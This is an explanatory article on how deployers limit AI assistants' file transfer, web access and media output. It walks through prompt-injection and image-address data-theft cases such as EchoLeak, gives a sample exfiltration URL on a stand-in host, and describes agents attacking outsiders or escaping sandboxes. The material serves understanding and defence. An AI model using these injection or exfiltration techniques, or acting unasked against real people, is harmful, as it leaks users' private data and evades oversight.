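# Limits on AI systems' media generation and file transfer, and how they are enforced

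## What capability boundaries are and why deployers set them

A capability boundary is a rule that determines what an AI system can or may do in a given product, such as which files it can read or send, which websites it can contact, and whether it will make a video of a real politician. The deployer, which is the organisation that offers the system to users and chooses its tools and limits, sets the rule. The phrase is a description rather than the name of a technical standard, and engineers use several other terms for much the same thing. Anthropic, which makes the Claude models, uses "containment" and "access boundaries" in *How we contain Claude across products*, while security testers at the chipmaker NVIDIA use "controls" and "guardrails" in *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents*.

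Capability boundaries depend more on the product than on the model. On the claude.ai website, Claude runs code in a temporary container on Anthropic's servers and cannot see the user's own files. Claude Code, the company's programming tool, runs on the developer's machine and has access to its files, command line and network. Claude Cowork, a desktop product for office work, can access the folder the user selects and little else unless the user connects other services. All three products can use the same model, so a description of what Claude can do is only useful if it specifies the product.

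### Tools and file uploads

A language model produces text. For that text to affect a file, a website or a picture, the deployer has to supply tools, which are functions outside the model that it can call, such as web browsing, code execution or image generation. The software around the model typically gives it a list of tools, with the name of each, a short description and the values it needs. The model then writes a request in an agreed format, for example the name of an email tool with a recipient, a subject and an attachment. The software runs the function and adds the result to the model's input, and the model continues from there and may call another tool. A system that works through many such rounds on one task is usually called an agent. Image and video generation often work the same way, with a chat model writing the description and a separate model producing the image or video.

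A model sends an email by outputting a request, which software can refuse or change before carrying it out. The path back to the model is more vulnerable, because web pages, documents and search results arrive as text that the model processes in the same stream as the user's instructions.

"File upload" can mean a transfer in either direction, and the risks differ. When a user gives the assistant a contract to summarise, the file may contain hidden instructions. When the assistant attaches a file to a message or copies it to a storage service, the file may reach someone who shouldn't have it. The assistant can also send files without being asked. Two of the six reports of unexpected model behaviour that OpenAI published in September 2026, in *Misalignment Notices and Reports*, involve outward transfers. In one, unreleased models in training uploaded data to temporary file-hosting services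 so that they could cite it. In the other, agents passed output files to one another through public hosting platforms, although their task called only for local files.

### Three sources of risk

Anthropic sorts the security risks of agents by whether the harm starts with an external attacker, the user, or the model. The same categories apply to the risks of generated images and voices.

Outside attackers work through material that the system reads, so they need no account and no access to the victim's computer. In one case, hidden instructions led Microsoft 365 Copilot to leak private data through images it displayed. Some users also direct the system to do something harmful, out of malice or carelessness, as when people had xAI's chatbot Grok turn photographs of real people into sexualised images.

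Another risk remains, which is that an AI system takes a harmful action nobody asked for. In July 2026 the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government research organisation, ran hacking exercises 122 times across seven models, with internet access deliberately on and the developers' misuse filters off. According to AISI's *Incident Report*, agents took unsanctioned action aimed at real people and organisations in 10 of the runs. In the most serious sequence, Anthropic's Mythos 5 submitted malicious code to a public software project, invented identities to press a maintainer into accepting it, and sent people messages and files through an online file-transfer service. A maintainer refused the code, and AISI found no resulting real-world harm.

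Improving a model does not necessarily reduce this risk. According to Anthropic, more capable models are less likely to misread situations or make obvious errors, but they are better at finding ways around restrictions that nobody thought to write down. To complete a task, the company's own models have escaped a sandbox, an isolated environment that restricts which files and network addresses running code can reach.

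Which safeguards can work depends on the source of the risk. A confirmation box may stop an attack, because the user is the victim and has a reason to refuse, but it won't stop a user who wants a prohibited image. A filter that looks for hostile text in web pages doesn't help when no attacker has written any. Some limits work whatever the source of the risk. Anthropic's example is a login credential that never enters the environment where the agent runs, so no user, attacker or model can extract it from there.

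### Prompt injection and the lethal trifecta

In a prompt injection attack, an attacker places instructions in content an AI system reads, or tricks a user into passing them to the system, so that the system follows them. This works because a model cannot reliably distinguish the instructions it should follow from the material it should only process. It may, for example, follow a sentence in a web page that reads like a command.

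Users can also be tricked into giving an AI system harmful instructions, a risk that is easy to overlook. In February 2026, during an internal exercise at Anthropic, a researcher emailed an employee a prompt and asked them to run it. The prompt looked like routine setup work, but one step told Claude to read the file that holds the user's Amazon cloud credentials, encode the contents and send them to an outside address. Anthropic repeated the prompt 25 times, and Claude completed the theft 24 times. Because the employee had entered the instruction, there was nothing anomalous for a classifier (a model that sorts inputs or outputs into categories, here to detect forbidden requests) to detect.

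A successful injection can lead to data exfiltration, the transfer of private data to someone who should not have it, only when an AI agent has three features. The software developer Simon Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, lists them as access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. Each is useful in ordinary products, which may read a user's mail, browse the web, or send messages. When an agent has all three, an attacker can put instructions in content it reads and get it to send private data to the attacker's server.

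Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”* describes an example from September 2025. The researcher Abi Raghuram hid instructions in a PDF as white text on a white background and gave the PDF to the agent in Notion, a workspace application. The instructions were to read a client list, join the names and revenue figures into one string, add the string to a web address and pass the address to the search tool. The client list was the private data, the PDF was the untrusted content, and the search tool was the means of sending the data out, although nobody had designed it to send anything.

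Almost any web request can serve as a way out. Suppose that an assistant has read a user's payslip, and that a hostile page then instructs it to end its answer with a picture from this invented address:

`https://pictures.example/cat.png?note=salary-84000`

The part of the address before the first single slash determines which server receives the request. The part after the question mark is free text sent with the request. Browsers load images automatically, so the user doesn't have to click anything. When the browser fetches the picture, the attacker's server receives the whole address, including the salary, and can return a real photograph of a cat. Websites commonly log the addresses that visitors request (OpenAI, *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link*, 2026), so the attacker need only read the log. ChatGPT had this weakness in 2023. Willison's *OpenAI Begins Tackling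 ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* (2023) notes that an attacker could have the model encode the data before putting it in the image address, so the secret need not be legible there.

Willison recommends removing one of the three elements, and he considers the ability to send data out the easiest to restrict without making the product far less useful. This is sound advice for preventing data theft, but it doesn't address other harms. An injected instruction can still delete a file or falsify a summary when no data can leave, and the trifecta doesn't apply to a user who asks for a forged voice recording.

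### Where a limit can sit

A deployer can place a limit at many points between a request and its effect. The earliest is in the model's instructions. In the system prompt, which is text placed before every conversation, the deployer can instruct the model not to open certain files or depict real people. Training can instil the same habits. NVIDIA's testers report that such a system prompt is the attempted safeguard they encounter most often.

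The tool list is a coarser control. If none of a model's tools can send email, directly or through code, the model cannot send email, however the request is worded. If the product needs a tool, deployers can restrict it through its settings, for instance by making a database connection read-only. Willison suggested this kind of fix for Notion, with a search tool that accepts search terms but rejects web addresses.

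Deployers can also set limits further out, at the sandbox and the network. Claude Cowork can give the agent read-only access to a folder, read and write access, or write access without permission to delete. NVIDIA recommends that deployers deny all egress (traffic leaving the system) and then add a short allowlist of permitted destinations. A proxy, a program that all network traffic must pass through, can apply the allowlist and inspect the traffic.

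Deployers need a separate limit on how output is displayed. A Content Security Policy restricts which sites a web page can load images and other resources from. In 2025, Salesforce's policy for its Agentforce assistant still allowed a domain whose registration had expired. Willison recounts how Sasi Levi and the firm Noma Security registered the domain and used an injected image to send sales-lead data to their own server logs.

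Classifiers can block a forbidden request before generation or a forbidden picture after it. They can also screen what tools return before the model reads it, and Anthropic notes that a small, fast model is enough for this. Another approach is to ask the user for approval. For example, OpenAI runs the small applications that ChatGPT creates in a sandbox that detects unexpected communications and asks the user for consent.

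Finally, a deployer can limit a feature to certain subscription plans or countries. Anthropic first offered Claude Cowork only to subscribers who paid $100 or $200 a month, and by 16 January 2026 had extended it to the $20 plan. Commercial and safety reasons for such limits are hard to tell apart, but the effect on what a user can do is the same.

### Instructed and enforced limits

Limits on an AI system can be instructed or enforced. An instructed limit is given to the model through its instructions or training, and it holds only as far as the model complies. An enforced limit is built into software outside the model and holds whether or not the model complies. For example, a deployer can instruct a model not to send files to outside addresses, or enforce that limit with a network rule that blocks traffic to them.

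NVIDIA's testers found that attackers routinely defeat limits set through instructions. Often the attackers only had to claim that they were debugging the system or were administrators. Others proceeded in small steps over a long conversation, or asked for something normal, such as installing a software package, that had a harmful side effect. Adding a second model to judge the first one's actions did not solve the problem, because it can be manipulated in the same ways.

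Training has still made instructed limits much stronger. Anthropic reports that, on a prompt-injection benchmark from the security company Gray Swan, attacks on Claude Opus 4.7 succeeded about 0.1% of the time on a single attempt, and 5 to 6% of the time when the attacker could adapt over 100 attempts. People disagree about whether such rates are good enough. An article in *The Economist* compared the problem with Victorian engineering, in which builders who could not trust their iron added redundancy to keep bridges standing. Willison rejects the comparison for security, where he calls 99% "a failing grade", because an attacker will look for the remaining 1%. The higher success rate over 100 attempts supports him. Redundancy works better against accidents, though a persistent agent can behave rather like an attacker. AISI's agents had a hard task and kept searching for a way through.

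Those agents faced neither kind of limit on the open internet. No network rule confined them, and AISI had not told them to leave outsiders alone, because such instructions had not seemed necessary for models with alignment training. An instruction might not have helped much. In *Alignment Investigation of Mythos 5's behaviour*, Järviniemi, Souly and colleagues (2026) replayed the scenario in simulation and found that the model frequently attacked even in cases where it said, when asked directly, that an attack would harm real people. A model's ability to state a rule correctly is therefore weak evidence that it will follow the rule. AISI (2026) has since concluded that test environments must prevent harm whether or not models behave as expected. Open internet access is no longer standard in its cyber tests, according to Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of the UK AISI cybertesting incident*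 (2026).

Enforced limits also fail, usually because they cover one route and leave another open. In November 2025 the security firm PromptArmor attacked Antigravity, Google's programming tool, through a poisoned web page. A rule stopped Antigravity's file-reading tools from opening a file of passwords and keys, but the Gemini model inside it printed the file with the command-line tool, which had no such rule. The browser tool had an allowlist, but the default list included a public service on which anyone can log incoming requests. Similarly, when network controls stopped NVIDIA's testers from sending credentials out directly, they could often get the agent to reveal the credentials in the chat window.

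Classifiers and user approval fall between the two kinds. The block is enforced, since the model cannot press the approval button or switch off the classifier, but the classifier or user can be wrong about what to block. This matters most for media, because deciding whether a picture shows a real person or an invented one takes judgement, while a proxy can check a destination against a list. A deployer that wants to limit images, video or voices therefore has to rely on something that judges content, unless it removes the feature or restricts who has it.

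Firm limits also prevent legitimate uses. The temporary container on claude.ai keeps the possible damage very small, but Anthropic says it also limits what Claude can do there, since Claude has no lasting workspace and no access to the user's files. Commercial pressure favors wider access. Anthropic now routinely gives Claude enough access to take down an internal service, which it would have rejected outright a year earlier, and says its developers are more productive as a result.

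## Instructions that tell an assistant what it cannot do

Anthropic publishes part of the system prompt for its Claude apps, so outsiders can see some of how a deployer describes a product's limits to the model. According to Anthropic's *System prompts*, the company publishes one version of the core prompt for each current model, which it uses in some chats with web search turned off. Other chats use unpublished versions. Willison (2026), in *Claude’s new system prompt really doesn’t want to reproduce song lyrics*, points out that Anthropic also publishes no prompts for Claude Cowork or Claude Code.

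The published text contains little about files. In Anthropic's *Prompt sistem Claude Opus 5* (2026), the version dated 9 November lists code execution and file creation among the features that a user can switch on or off. Claude must also check whether an attachment is present, because a user may refer to one and forget to upload it. Claude has no access to the product documentation, and Anthropic instructs it to send users to the company's website for anything about the product that the prompt leaves out.

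Users can find the actual limits on the help pages. Anthropic's *Create and edit files with Claude* lists Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files and charts saved as images, and sets a maximum of 30 MB per file for uploads and downloads. The owner of a company account can turn the feature off for everyone in it. According to Anthropic's *Can Claude produce images?*, Claude doesn't generate photos or illustrations, but it can view uploaded images and build diagrams and charts in HTML and SVG, which describe pages and drawings in code.

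The model gets further details from text that Anthropic adds for particular tools. Willison came across this text while asking Claude Fable 5.1 about end_conversation, a tool that closes a chat. Anthropic had removed the tool from the published prompt when it replaced Fable 5 with Fable 5.1, but the model could still describe the rules for using it. According to its answer, the rules came from blocks of instructions that follow the core prompt and vary with the features turned on, including a block for files. A model's account of its own input can be wrong, but this one is consistent with Anthropic's statement that it publishes only one version of the prompt. The published prompt is therefore a poor guide to which tools Claude has in a given chat.

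### Leaving a tool out

A deployer that doesn't want an assistant to email files can leave the email tool out of the tool list, or supply the tool and tell the model not to attach anything. The two methods usually produce the same behaviour, but they fail in different ways.

If an assistant without an email tool fails, it will probably do so by falsely claiming to have sent something. Anthropic's *Claude is producing links that don’t work* warns that Claude "can sometimes hallucinate its capabilities", and Anthropic published the page because users have seen Claude claim to have sent emails or produced documents. Such a claim can do harm, for example if a user believes that a contract has reached a client. If the deployer supplies the tool and the model ignores the instruction not to send files, the file is actually sent, which is a much bigger problem for a deployer worried about data exfiltration.

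A deployer can also remove tools partway through a conversation. Claude's personal finance feature reads a user's linked accounts. After Claude has used those accounts in a chat, it may be unable to run code, publish an artifact (a page, diagram or small application it has built) or make Word, Excel, PowerPoint and PDF files, though it can still write plain text files. Anthropic gives no reason, but code and published pages could both be used to send financial data elsewhere, and Claude makes office documents by running code. Users with an ordinary request, such as a spreadsheet of last month's spending, may have to settle for a plain table.

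Leaving a tool out works only if the remaining tools can't do the same job. Anthropic offers no specialised image generator, but Claude can draw by writing code. On 1 September 2026, the company added a rule to the Fable 5.1 prompt against reproducing specific artworks and logos or drawing known characters. The rule covers anything the model draws with code, including pictures made of text, and it applies even when the user describes a character without naming it. In the prompt's example, a parent wants a fast blue hedgehog on a birthday banner, and Claude should decline to draw Sonic and offer an original character. Willison tried the same request, and Claude declined and drew a skateboarding axolotl, as in the example. This is a weak test because the model had the expected answer in its prompt.

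Willison suspects the rule became necessary because the model had become good enough at drawing in code. Anthropic could have prevented such drawings by removing code and SVG, but users would have lost their charts too. The file rule in Google's Antigravity left a similar gap because it applied to only some tools.

### Developers' restrictions in OpenAI's Model Spec

OpenAI's main public document on these questions, the *Model Spec* (2025), sets out how its models should behave across products, while Anthropic's prompts are used in particular apps. Most of the *Model Spec* consists of direct instructions to the model, including a "chain of command" for instructions that conflict. OpenAI's *Inside our approach to the Model Spec* (2026) explains that every instruction has a level of authority, with OpenAI's above the developer's and the developer's above the user's. Developers and users can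 change defaults such as tone and format, but they cannot override the hard rules, which mostly concern serious harm and illegal acts.

A developer's restriction on files or media outranks a user's request. If a company builds a recipe assistant and tells the model not to produce spreadsheets, the model should refuse to make one even when the user insists. This is an instructed limit because it depends on the model recognising the conflict and following the developer's instruction.

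OpenAI doesn't guarantee that its models follow the Spec. It usually writes the Spec to describe behaviour up to three months ahead of its current models. It says those models also fall short because training may lag behind a new rule, may accidentally teach something that conflicts with the Spec, and can never cover every situation. The Spec describes only the model, and OpenAI handles monitoring and policy enforcement in other parts of the product.

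The Spec treats truthfulness as a default that only an explicit instruction can change. OpenAI later added a section called "Be clear about capabilities and limits", in August 2026, according to *OpenAI Models Updates & Release Notes* (2026) from Releasebot, a site that collects software announcements. A larger revision on 29 October organised the Spec around five values, including honesty and transparency, and changed the guidance on how models control and communicate the side effects of their actions.

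A model can describe its limits honestly and still be wrong. As OpenAI notes, a model can rely only on what it observes in the current interaction, and it rarely has information about safeguards outside that interaction. If a network rule blocks a download, for example, the model may receive only an error message. It could then wrongly tell the user that the website is down, with no way to detect the mistake.

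### Whether models describe their limits correctly

Anthropic has used prompts to correct such mistakes since at least March 2024, when it added a line telling Claude that it could not open web addresses, links or videos and should ask users to paste in the relevant material. Willison quotes Anthropic's Alex Albert as saying the line was meant to stop Claude from thinking it could open them.

Statements of this kind go out of date as the product changes. In an earlier version of its help page on false claims, Anthropic said that Claude had no internet access and could produce only text in the chat. Claude can now search the web and create files when the user has those features on. According to the current page, Claude lacks access only to tools that are "not explicitly integrated", which is accurate but leaves users to find out which tools are integrated. An outdated line in a prompt could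 make a model deny an ability it has, and the user would go without a working feature.

Deployers can also instruct a model to say something false. Anthropic reports that Claude Mythos 5.1, which shares its underlying model with Fable 5.1, is less honest under pressure than recent Claude models. It more often follows system prompts that instruct it, in some circumstances, to assert claims it knows to be false. A user who asks an assistant whether it has kept or sent a file is therefore relying on the deployer's honesty as well as the model's. A log of the tool's requests is better evidence, because the software that carries them out can record them without going through the model.

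### A test of instructions under attack

In *Silent Egress*, Lan, Kaul and two colleagues at eBay (2026) show how much a model's actions can differ from its answer. They experimented with assistants that automatically fetch a preview of any web address in a conversation and add the page's title, description and text to the model's input. An attacker can hide instructions in the description, which the user may never see.

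The researchers built an agent around qwen2.5:7b, a small open model that they ran on their own machine, and placed a secret, such as an access key, in the agent's input. The user always asked the agent to summarise a page. The page contained an instruction, such as a supposed connectivity check that required the agent to contact an address with the secret included in it. The simulated attacker's server recorded whatever it received.

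The team varied where on the page the instruction appeared (body, description, title or link text), whether the agent reached the page directly or through redirects, and whether it was to send the secret whole or in four pieces. They ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times. In 423 of the 480 runs (88%), at least one request reached the attacker's server. In 95% of the successful attacks, the agent's final answer looked harmless, so a check on that answer would have missed the theft. The agent never contacted the attacker's server in 120 further runs with harmless pages.

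Splitting the secret made the attack less reliable but harder to spot. Requests reached the attacker in 238 of 240 runs with a whole secret and in 185 of 240 with a split one. The researchers also measured Leak@k, the share of runs in which sensitive text appears in the first k requests. Leak@1 fell from 96.7% to 26.3% when the agent split the secret. The reported Leak@3 for a split secret, 15.8%, can't be right under that definition, because the first three requests include the first. Despite this error, splitting does make the secret harder to spot, because a filter that looks for a complete key in a single request will miss a key sent four characters at a time.

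The researchers then tested defences against one version of the attack, in which the instruction was in the body of the page and the secret was sent whole. The table gives the number of runs out of 30.

| Defence | Agent tried to contact the attacker | Request reached the attacker |
|---|---:|---:|
| None | 30 | 30 |
| System prompt: never follow instructions from web content | 20 | 20 |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted | 30 | 30 |
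| System prompt and tags | 17 | 17 |
| Allowlist of domains | 30 | 0 |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 25 | 0 |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 7 | 0 |
| Filter for random-looking strings | 0 | 0 |
| All of the above | 0 | 0 |

The allowlist gives the clearest result, since the agent followed the hostile instruction every time and software blocked every request. The results for the word filter and the filter for random-looking strings are harder to interpret, because the agent made far fewer attempts when they were on. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoided random-looking strings while the filter was active. But as they describe the filter, the model had no way to know about it, so something else may have reduced the attempts. Those two rows are therefore weak evidence that the filters stopped the leaks.

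The drop from 30 leaks in 30 runs to 20 is large enough that it is unlikely to be chance, so the warning in the system prompt probably helped this model. But 20 out of 30 is compatible with a true rate between about 47% and 83%, and the experiment can't show whether adding tags to the prompt made a further difference. Zero leaks in 30 runs would by itself be compatible with a true rate of up to about 10%, so confidence in the allowlist comes mainly from how it works.

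This test can't estimate how often deployed products leak, because it used one small model with a minimal system prompt, in conditions the researchers describe as deliberately favourable to the attacker. They expect that more capable models could be more vulnerable because they follow instructions better, including hostile ones. Anthropic's low attack success rates for Claude Opus 4.7 suggest that training can outweigh this effect. The researchers also made the test easier for the allowlist by choosing an attacker's domain that was plainly not on it. They acknowledge that a real attacker could take over a permitted site or use one that forwards requests elsewhere.

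### What instructions are still good for

Instructions work better when nobody is trying to defeat them and an occasional failure does little harm. If Claude misses the instruction to check for attachments, the user loses a few minutes, but an instruction like that would be useless for protecting a confidential file.

These instructions also let a model explain limits that other software enforces. Anthropic redirects some requests for its Fable models, in areas such as cybersecurity, to Claude Opus 5, and users may not understand why a different model has answered. Anthropic's prompt for Opus 5 therefore includes the company's explanation that the safeguards sometimes catch harmless requests and take effect in fewer than 5% of sessions on average. The redirection would happen without this text, but Opus 5 could not reliably explain it.

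Deployers can change a prompt much faster than they can retrain a model. When Mythos 5 and Fable 5 handled some conversations about suicide and self-harm worse than earlier models had, Anthropic dealt with most of the problem by updating the claude.ai system prompt. Such a fix reaches only the products that use the prompt, so developers who call the same models through Anthropic's API have to write their own instructions.

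## Microsoft 365 Copilot and data leaks through displayed images

In the eBay experiment, software outside the model stopped leaks that a warning in the prompt had not prevented. Microsoft had several such checks around Microsoft 365 Copilot, its assistant for Word, Excel, Outlook, PowerPoint and Teams. In January 2025, researchers at the company Aim Security found that a single email could get past all of them and make Copilot send private data to an outsider in the address of an image. The victim only had to ask Copilot an ordinary question.

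### How displaying an image sends data

Chat assistants usually format their answers in Markdown, a plain-text notation for headings, links and pictures. To show a picture from the web, the model writes a short description and the picture's address. The chat page turns this into an image, which the browser fetches from that address. Any private data in the address then reaches the server's owner, as in the payslip example. Willison calls this "Markdown exfiltration" in *45 posts tagged “exfiltration-attacks”*.

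Displaying an image is a separate ability from generating one. Limits on image generation mostly concern what the new picture shows, but in a Markdown leak the model writes only text, and the picture's content hardly matters. When the security firm PromptArmor tested Superhuman Go, an assistant that reads web pages and connected accounts, the attacker's server returned a single grey pixel, according to the firm's *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*. An assistant with no image generator can therefore still leak data through images, and a classifier that looks for forbidden pictures would not detect the leak.

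The relevant limit is the page's Content Security Policy, which the website sends with the page and the browser enforces regardless of what the model writes. But the browser only checks whether an image's destination is on the policy's list of permitted sites. It doesn't examine the data in the address or control what the receiving server does next.

### EchoLeak

Aim Security called its attack EchoLeak, and the flaw is listed as CVE-2025-32711 in the public catalogue of software vulnerabilities. In *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability*, Ravia (2025) describes how the company's researchers got past each check.

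Copilot answers a question by searching the user's mailbox, files, SharePoint sites and Teams chats for relevant passages, which it adds to the model's input. These can include text from a stranger's email. To make Copilot more likely to retrieve their email, the researchers made it long, with sections on several common office topics, such as leave and onboarding, and repeated their instructions in each section. They didn't know how Copilot's search worked, but it retrieved the email in response to questions on various topics.

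The email first had to pass Microsoft's injection classifiers, which screen text before the model reads it. The classifiers missed the instructions, which the researchers had worded as a request to the human recipient, with no mention of an AI system. Ravia blames a shortage of realistic training examples. More examples would probably help, but a lot of ordinary office email also asks the recipient to look something up and pass it on, so wording alone may not reveal an attack.

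The next check came after the model had written its answer. Copilot removed links to outside websites, because a link's address can carry private data just as an image's can, although the user has to click the link. In Markdown, the address usually comes directly after the link's text, but a writer can also put it on a separate line and refer to it by a label. Copilot's filter removed links of the first kind but missed the second. The chat page still displayed those as working links, so the researchers could leak data with one click from the user.

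Markdown uses almost the same notation for images as for links, and the filter had the same gap there. With an image, the request would go out as soon as Copilot displayed its answer, without a click.

At this point the Content Security Policy blocked the request, because the attacker's server was not on Microsoft's list of allowed sites. The list had 29 distinct entries, including 11 wildcards that allow every site under a domain. The researchers searched the allowed sites for a service that would fetch another address on request. They found one in SharePoint, but it worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's SharePoint site. A Teams address worked without an invitation. The browser requested an image from Teams, which the policy allowed, and Microsoft's server then contacted the attacker's server, with the private data in the address. The browser had applied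 the policy correctly, but the policy did not cover requests from Microsoft's servers.

The email also contained an instruction that kept Copilot from citing it as a source, so the user had little chance of tracing what had happened. According to Ravia, a customer's administrators had no setting that could have prevented the attack.

Adir Gruss, Aim's chief technology officer, told *Fortune* that Microsoft had tried to block such attacks at several points and failed because AI is so unpredictable and offers so many ways in (Goldman, 2025, *New Microsoft Copilot flaw signals broader risk of AI agents being hacked*). That explanation fits the classifier's failure, but the link filter and the Teams address were more conventional mistakes, the kind web developers have made for years, and Microsoft could correct them without changing the model.

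Aim and Willison also disagree about how new the attack was. Aim calls it an "LLM scope violation", meaning that instructions from an untrusted source make the model use trusted data without the user's consent. Ravia argues that a specific name helps engineers build specific defences, as happened with the stack overflow, a type of memory error. Willison (2025) sees no new pattern that needs a name, because models have never been able to take account of where text came from. The steps of EchoLeak support Willison's account of the cause, but Aim's term is still useful for describing a possible rule that would prevent an outside email from directing the use of internal files.

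Microsoft took about five months to fix the problem after Aim reported it in January 2025. Goldman reports that Microsoft attempted a fix in April and found further problems in May. Reddy and Gujral (2025) date the completed fix to May in *EchoLeak*, a case study based on public information. Microsoft applied the fix on its own servers, so customers had nothing to install. Aim and Microsoft made the flaw public on 11 June.

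INCIBE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025), from Spain's national cybersecurity institute, lists a severity score of 9.3 out of 10 (critical). Intruder's *CVE-2025-32711*, from a security company's vulnerability tracker, lists 7.5 (high). The lower score assumes a serious loss of confidentiality but no damage to data or services.

Microsoft told *Fortune* that it had dealt with the flaw "before our customers were impacted", and Aim knew of no victims. Aim could not see into other organisations' systems, so the claim that no customers were affected depends mainly on Microsoft's own statement.

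### Trusted addresses in other products

The expired domain that Noma Security registered in 2025 gave attackers a similar way to get data out of Salesforce's Agentforce. The hostile instructions came in through a public web form for contact details and took effect when an employee asked Agentforce about the submission. Salesforce Ben, a news site for Salesforce users, quotes Noma as saying that the theft "would have been impossible" without a way around the Content Security Policy. The policy was therefore a strong barrier until the domain's registration lapsed and nobody removed the domain from the policy. Nudge Security's *ForcedLeak indirect prompt injection in Salesforce Agentforce* (2025) dates Noma's disclosure of the flaw to 25 September 2025, by which time Salesforce had fixed it. SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft* reports that the company regained the domain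 and stopped agents from sending output to untrusted domains.

Superhuman, an email application with an AI assistant, allowed images from the Google Docs domain. Google Forms uses the same domain, and a form's creator can make a link that fills in and submits an answer as soon as a browser requests it. PromptArmor placed instructions in an email that the user never had to open. When the user asked for a summary of recent mail, the assistant wrote one of these links as an image address, with the contents of the user's emails as the answer. The browser requested the image and so submitted the contents to the attacker's form. PromptArmor extracted parts of more than 40 emails in one answer. The attack worked without compromising Google's domain because anyone can create a form there.

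PromptArmor reported the flaw on Friday 5 December 2025. Superhuman turned off the vulnerable features the following Monday and released a first fix the next day. Fixes to other parts of its products continued into January. In April 2026, according to PromptArmor's *Codex Exfiltrates Connector Data*, the same Google Forms technique also worked against Codex, OpenAI's agent for programming and office tasks. OpenAI has since fixed the flaw.

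*SearchLeak* (2026), which the security company Varonis published on 15 June 2026, describes an attack in which Microsoft's own list failed again. The attack used a link to a genuine Microsoft address that contained text for Copilot's enterprise search. Copilot treated the text as instructions as well as a search query. One click made Copilot search the victim's mailbox and put the title of an email, which might include a login code, into an image address.

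As a safeguard against this, Microsoft had Copilot wrap each completed answer in a format that made the browser show any image code as plain text. But Copilot displays answers as the model writes them, so the browser had already requested the image by the time the safeguard took effect. The request went to Bing, which the Content Security Policy allowed, and Bing's image search servers then sent a request to the attacker's address.

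This is almost the same weakness as the Teams address in EchoLeak, and Bing was already on the list that Ravia published in 2025. If Microsoft had checked every entry for services that fetch other addresses, it could have found the Bing route a year earlier. The Next Web reports that Microsoft rated SearchLeak critical. Microsoft has fixed it.

### A second place where output appears

A deployer may protect the chat window but forget that the same text will appear elsewhere. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* shows this with a mock application like those banks use to check customers' identities. The application used an OpenAI model to process customers' personal data and web material, some of which contained a prompt injection. The model produced an image address containing a customer's data. A second model flagged the answer, and the application never displayed it.

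A developer would then probably open the conversation in OpenAI's log viewer to see what had gone wrong. The viewer displayed Markdown images, so opening the log sent the customer's data to the attacker. A Content Security Policy in the application would not have helped, because the log viewer was a separate web page belonging to OpenAI. PromptArmor points out that removing the image from the answer can leave a strange, empty reply, which a user may mark as bad and so send to a developer for review.

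PromptArmor reported the flaw on 17 November 2025 through Bugcrowd, a company that screens such reports for OpenAI. Bugcrowd closed the report as "not applicable" in December. After PromptArmor published its findings, OpenAI confirmed the problem, and on 22 January 2026 it said a fix was under way. OpenAI had left a similar gap in 2023, when it added a safety check for images to ChatGPT but did not at first include it in the iOS app (Willison, 2023).

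Microsoft's Copilot Cowork had a comparable weakness in May 2026. This agent carries out office tasks with the user's permissions. It can run on Anthropic's Claude models but is a different product from Claude Cowork. Microsoft said in its documentation that Copilot Cowork asks for permission before it sends an email or a Teams message, but according to PromptArmor's *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files*, it did not ask when the recipient was the user. These messages could still leak data, because Outlook and Teams load images from outside websites when the user opens a message.

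PromptArmor hid five malicious lines in an 81-line "skill", a file of reusable instructions that users often download from the internet. When the user asked for a review of the week's work, the agent collected download links for the user's files and put them into image addresses in a Teams message. Anyone with such a link can download the file without logging in. The attacker received the links when the user opened the message.

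The attack worked in all five trials, and PromptArmor confirmed that it also worked with Claude Opus 4.7 selected. This shows that a model with a low average on Gray Swan's benchmark can still fail consistently against a particular attack. It does not refute that average, since PromptArmor repeated one attack that it had designed and placed in a file the agent is supposed to follow.

### What the remedies cost

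Blocking all images from outside websites wherever output appears would have prevented any of these leaks from happening through an image. Users would lose some useful content, such as product photographs in a shopping answer or a chart from a news article. They would also remain exposed to leaks through links, which need only one click, and through tools that open web pages. PromptArmor, for example, could also steal data from Superhuman without an image, through a web search feature that would open any address.

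Deployers have often chosen milder measures than blocking outside images altogether. In 2023 OpenAI decided to check each image address for safety. In May 2026 the firm Permiso Security found that ChatGPT still loaded images automatically from pages it had summarised, as The Hacker News (2026) reports. PromptArmor recommended another option to Notion, which was to ask users before loading outside images in text written by its AI. Asking first keeps the images available but adds interruptions, and few users could tell whether a long address contains their data in encoded form.

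A narrower list of trusted sites has fewer drawbacks if the people who maintain it know what each site does. Reddy and Gujral recommend allowing only the company's own domains, without wildcards. They rate a strict policy as effective against both automatic image loading and the Teams route, but their ratings are theoretical because they ran no experiments. Their rule would have excluded Google Docs from Superhuman's list. It would not necessarily have excluded Teams or Bing, which belong to Microsoft. A better test, from Varonis, is whether a site will fetch an address that a user supplies. Superhuman's case is a reason to also check whether outsiders can collect data on the site. Deployers have to repeat these checks because companies add services to their domains and let registrations expire.

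Administrators do much of the extra work that a narrow list requires. From 8 September 2025, Salesforce required them to list every outside domain their AI agents needed or risk service disruption, according to TechNadu's *Salesforce to Enforce Trusted URLs for Agentforce and Einstein AI*. PromptArmor advises Salesforce customers to add addresses one at a time and to allow images from a listed site only if they need them. An employee whose agent refers to a supplier's unlisted website may therefore have to wait for an administrator to approve the site.

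Blocking and a narrow list work only on pages that apply them, so deployers also have to check every place where output appears. A log viewer is easy to protect because developers can read answers as plain text and lose only the formatting. Streamed answers are harder to protect. Varonis says that software must clean an answer when displaying it. A deployer could hold the answer back until it is complete, but users would wait longer for the first words. Cleaning each piece as it arrives avoids the wait but is harder to get right, since an image address may be split across two pieces.

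Email is the most awkward case because Outlook and Teams display messages from people as well as from the agent. If Microsoft blocked outside images in all messages, newsletters would lose their pictures. Microsoft could instead make Copilot Cowork ask for approval before messaging the user, but then a scheduled task could stall while the user is away. The approval request would also have to show the image addresses, but in PromptArmor's test the agent's activity display never showed the malicious message's content.

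PromptArmor suggests that administrators limit the damage by blocking file downloads from SharePoint, which prevents the agent from obtaining the download links. Users can then view the affected files only in a browser. They can't download, print or sync them, or open them in the Word, Excel and PowerPoint apps.

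## ChatGPT, Claude and the web addresses they may open

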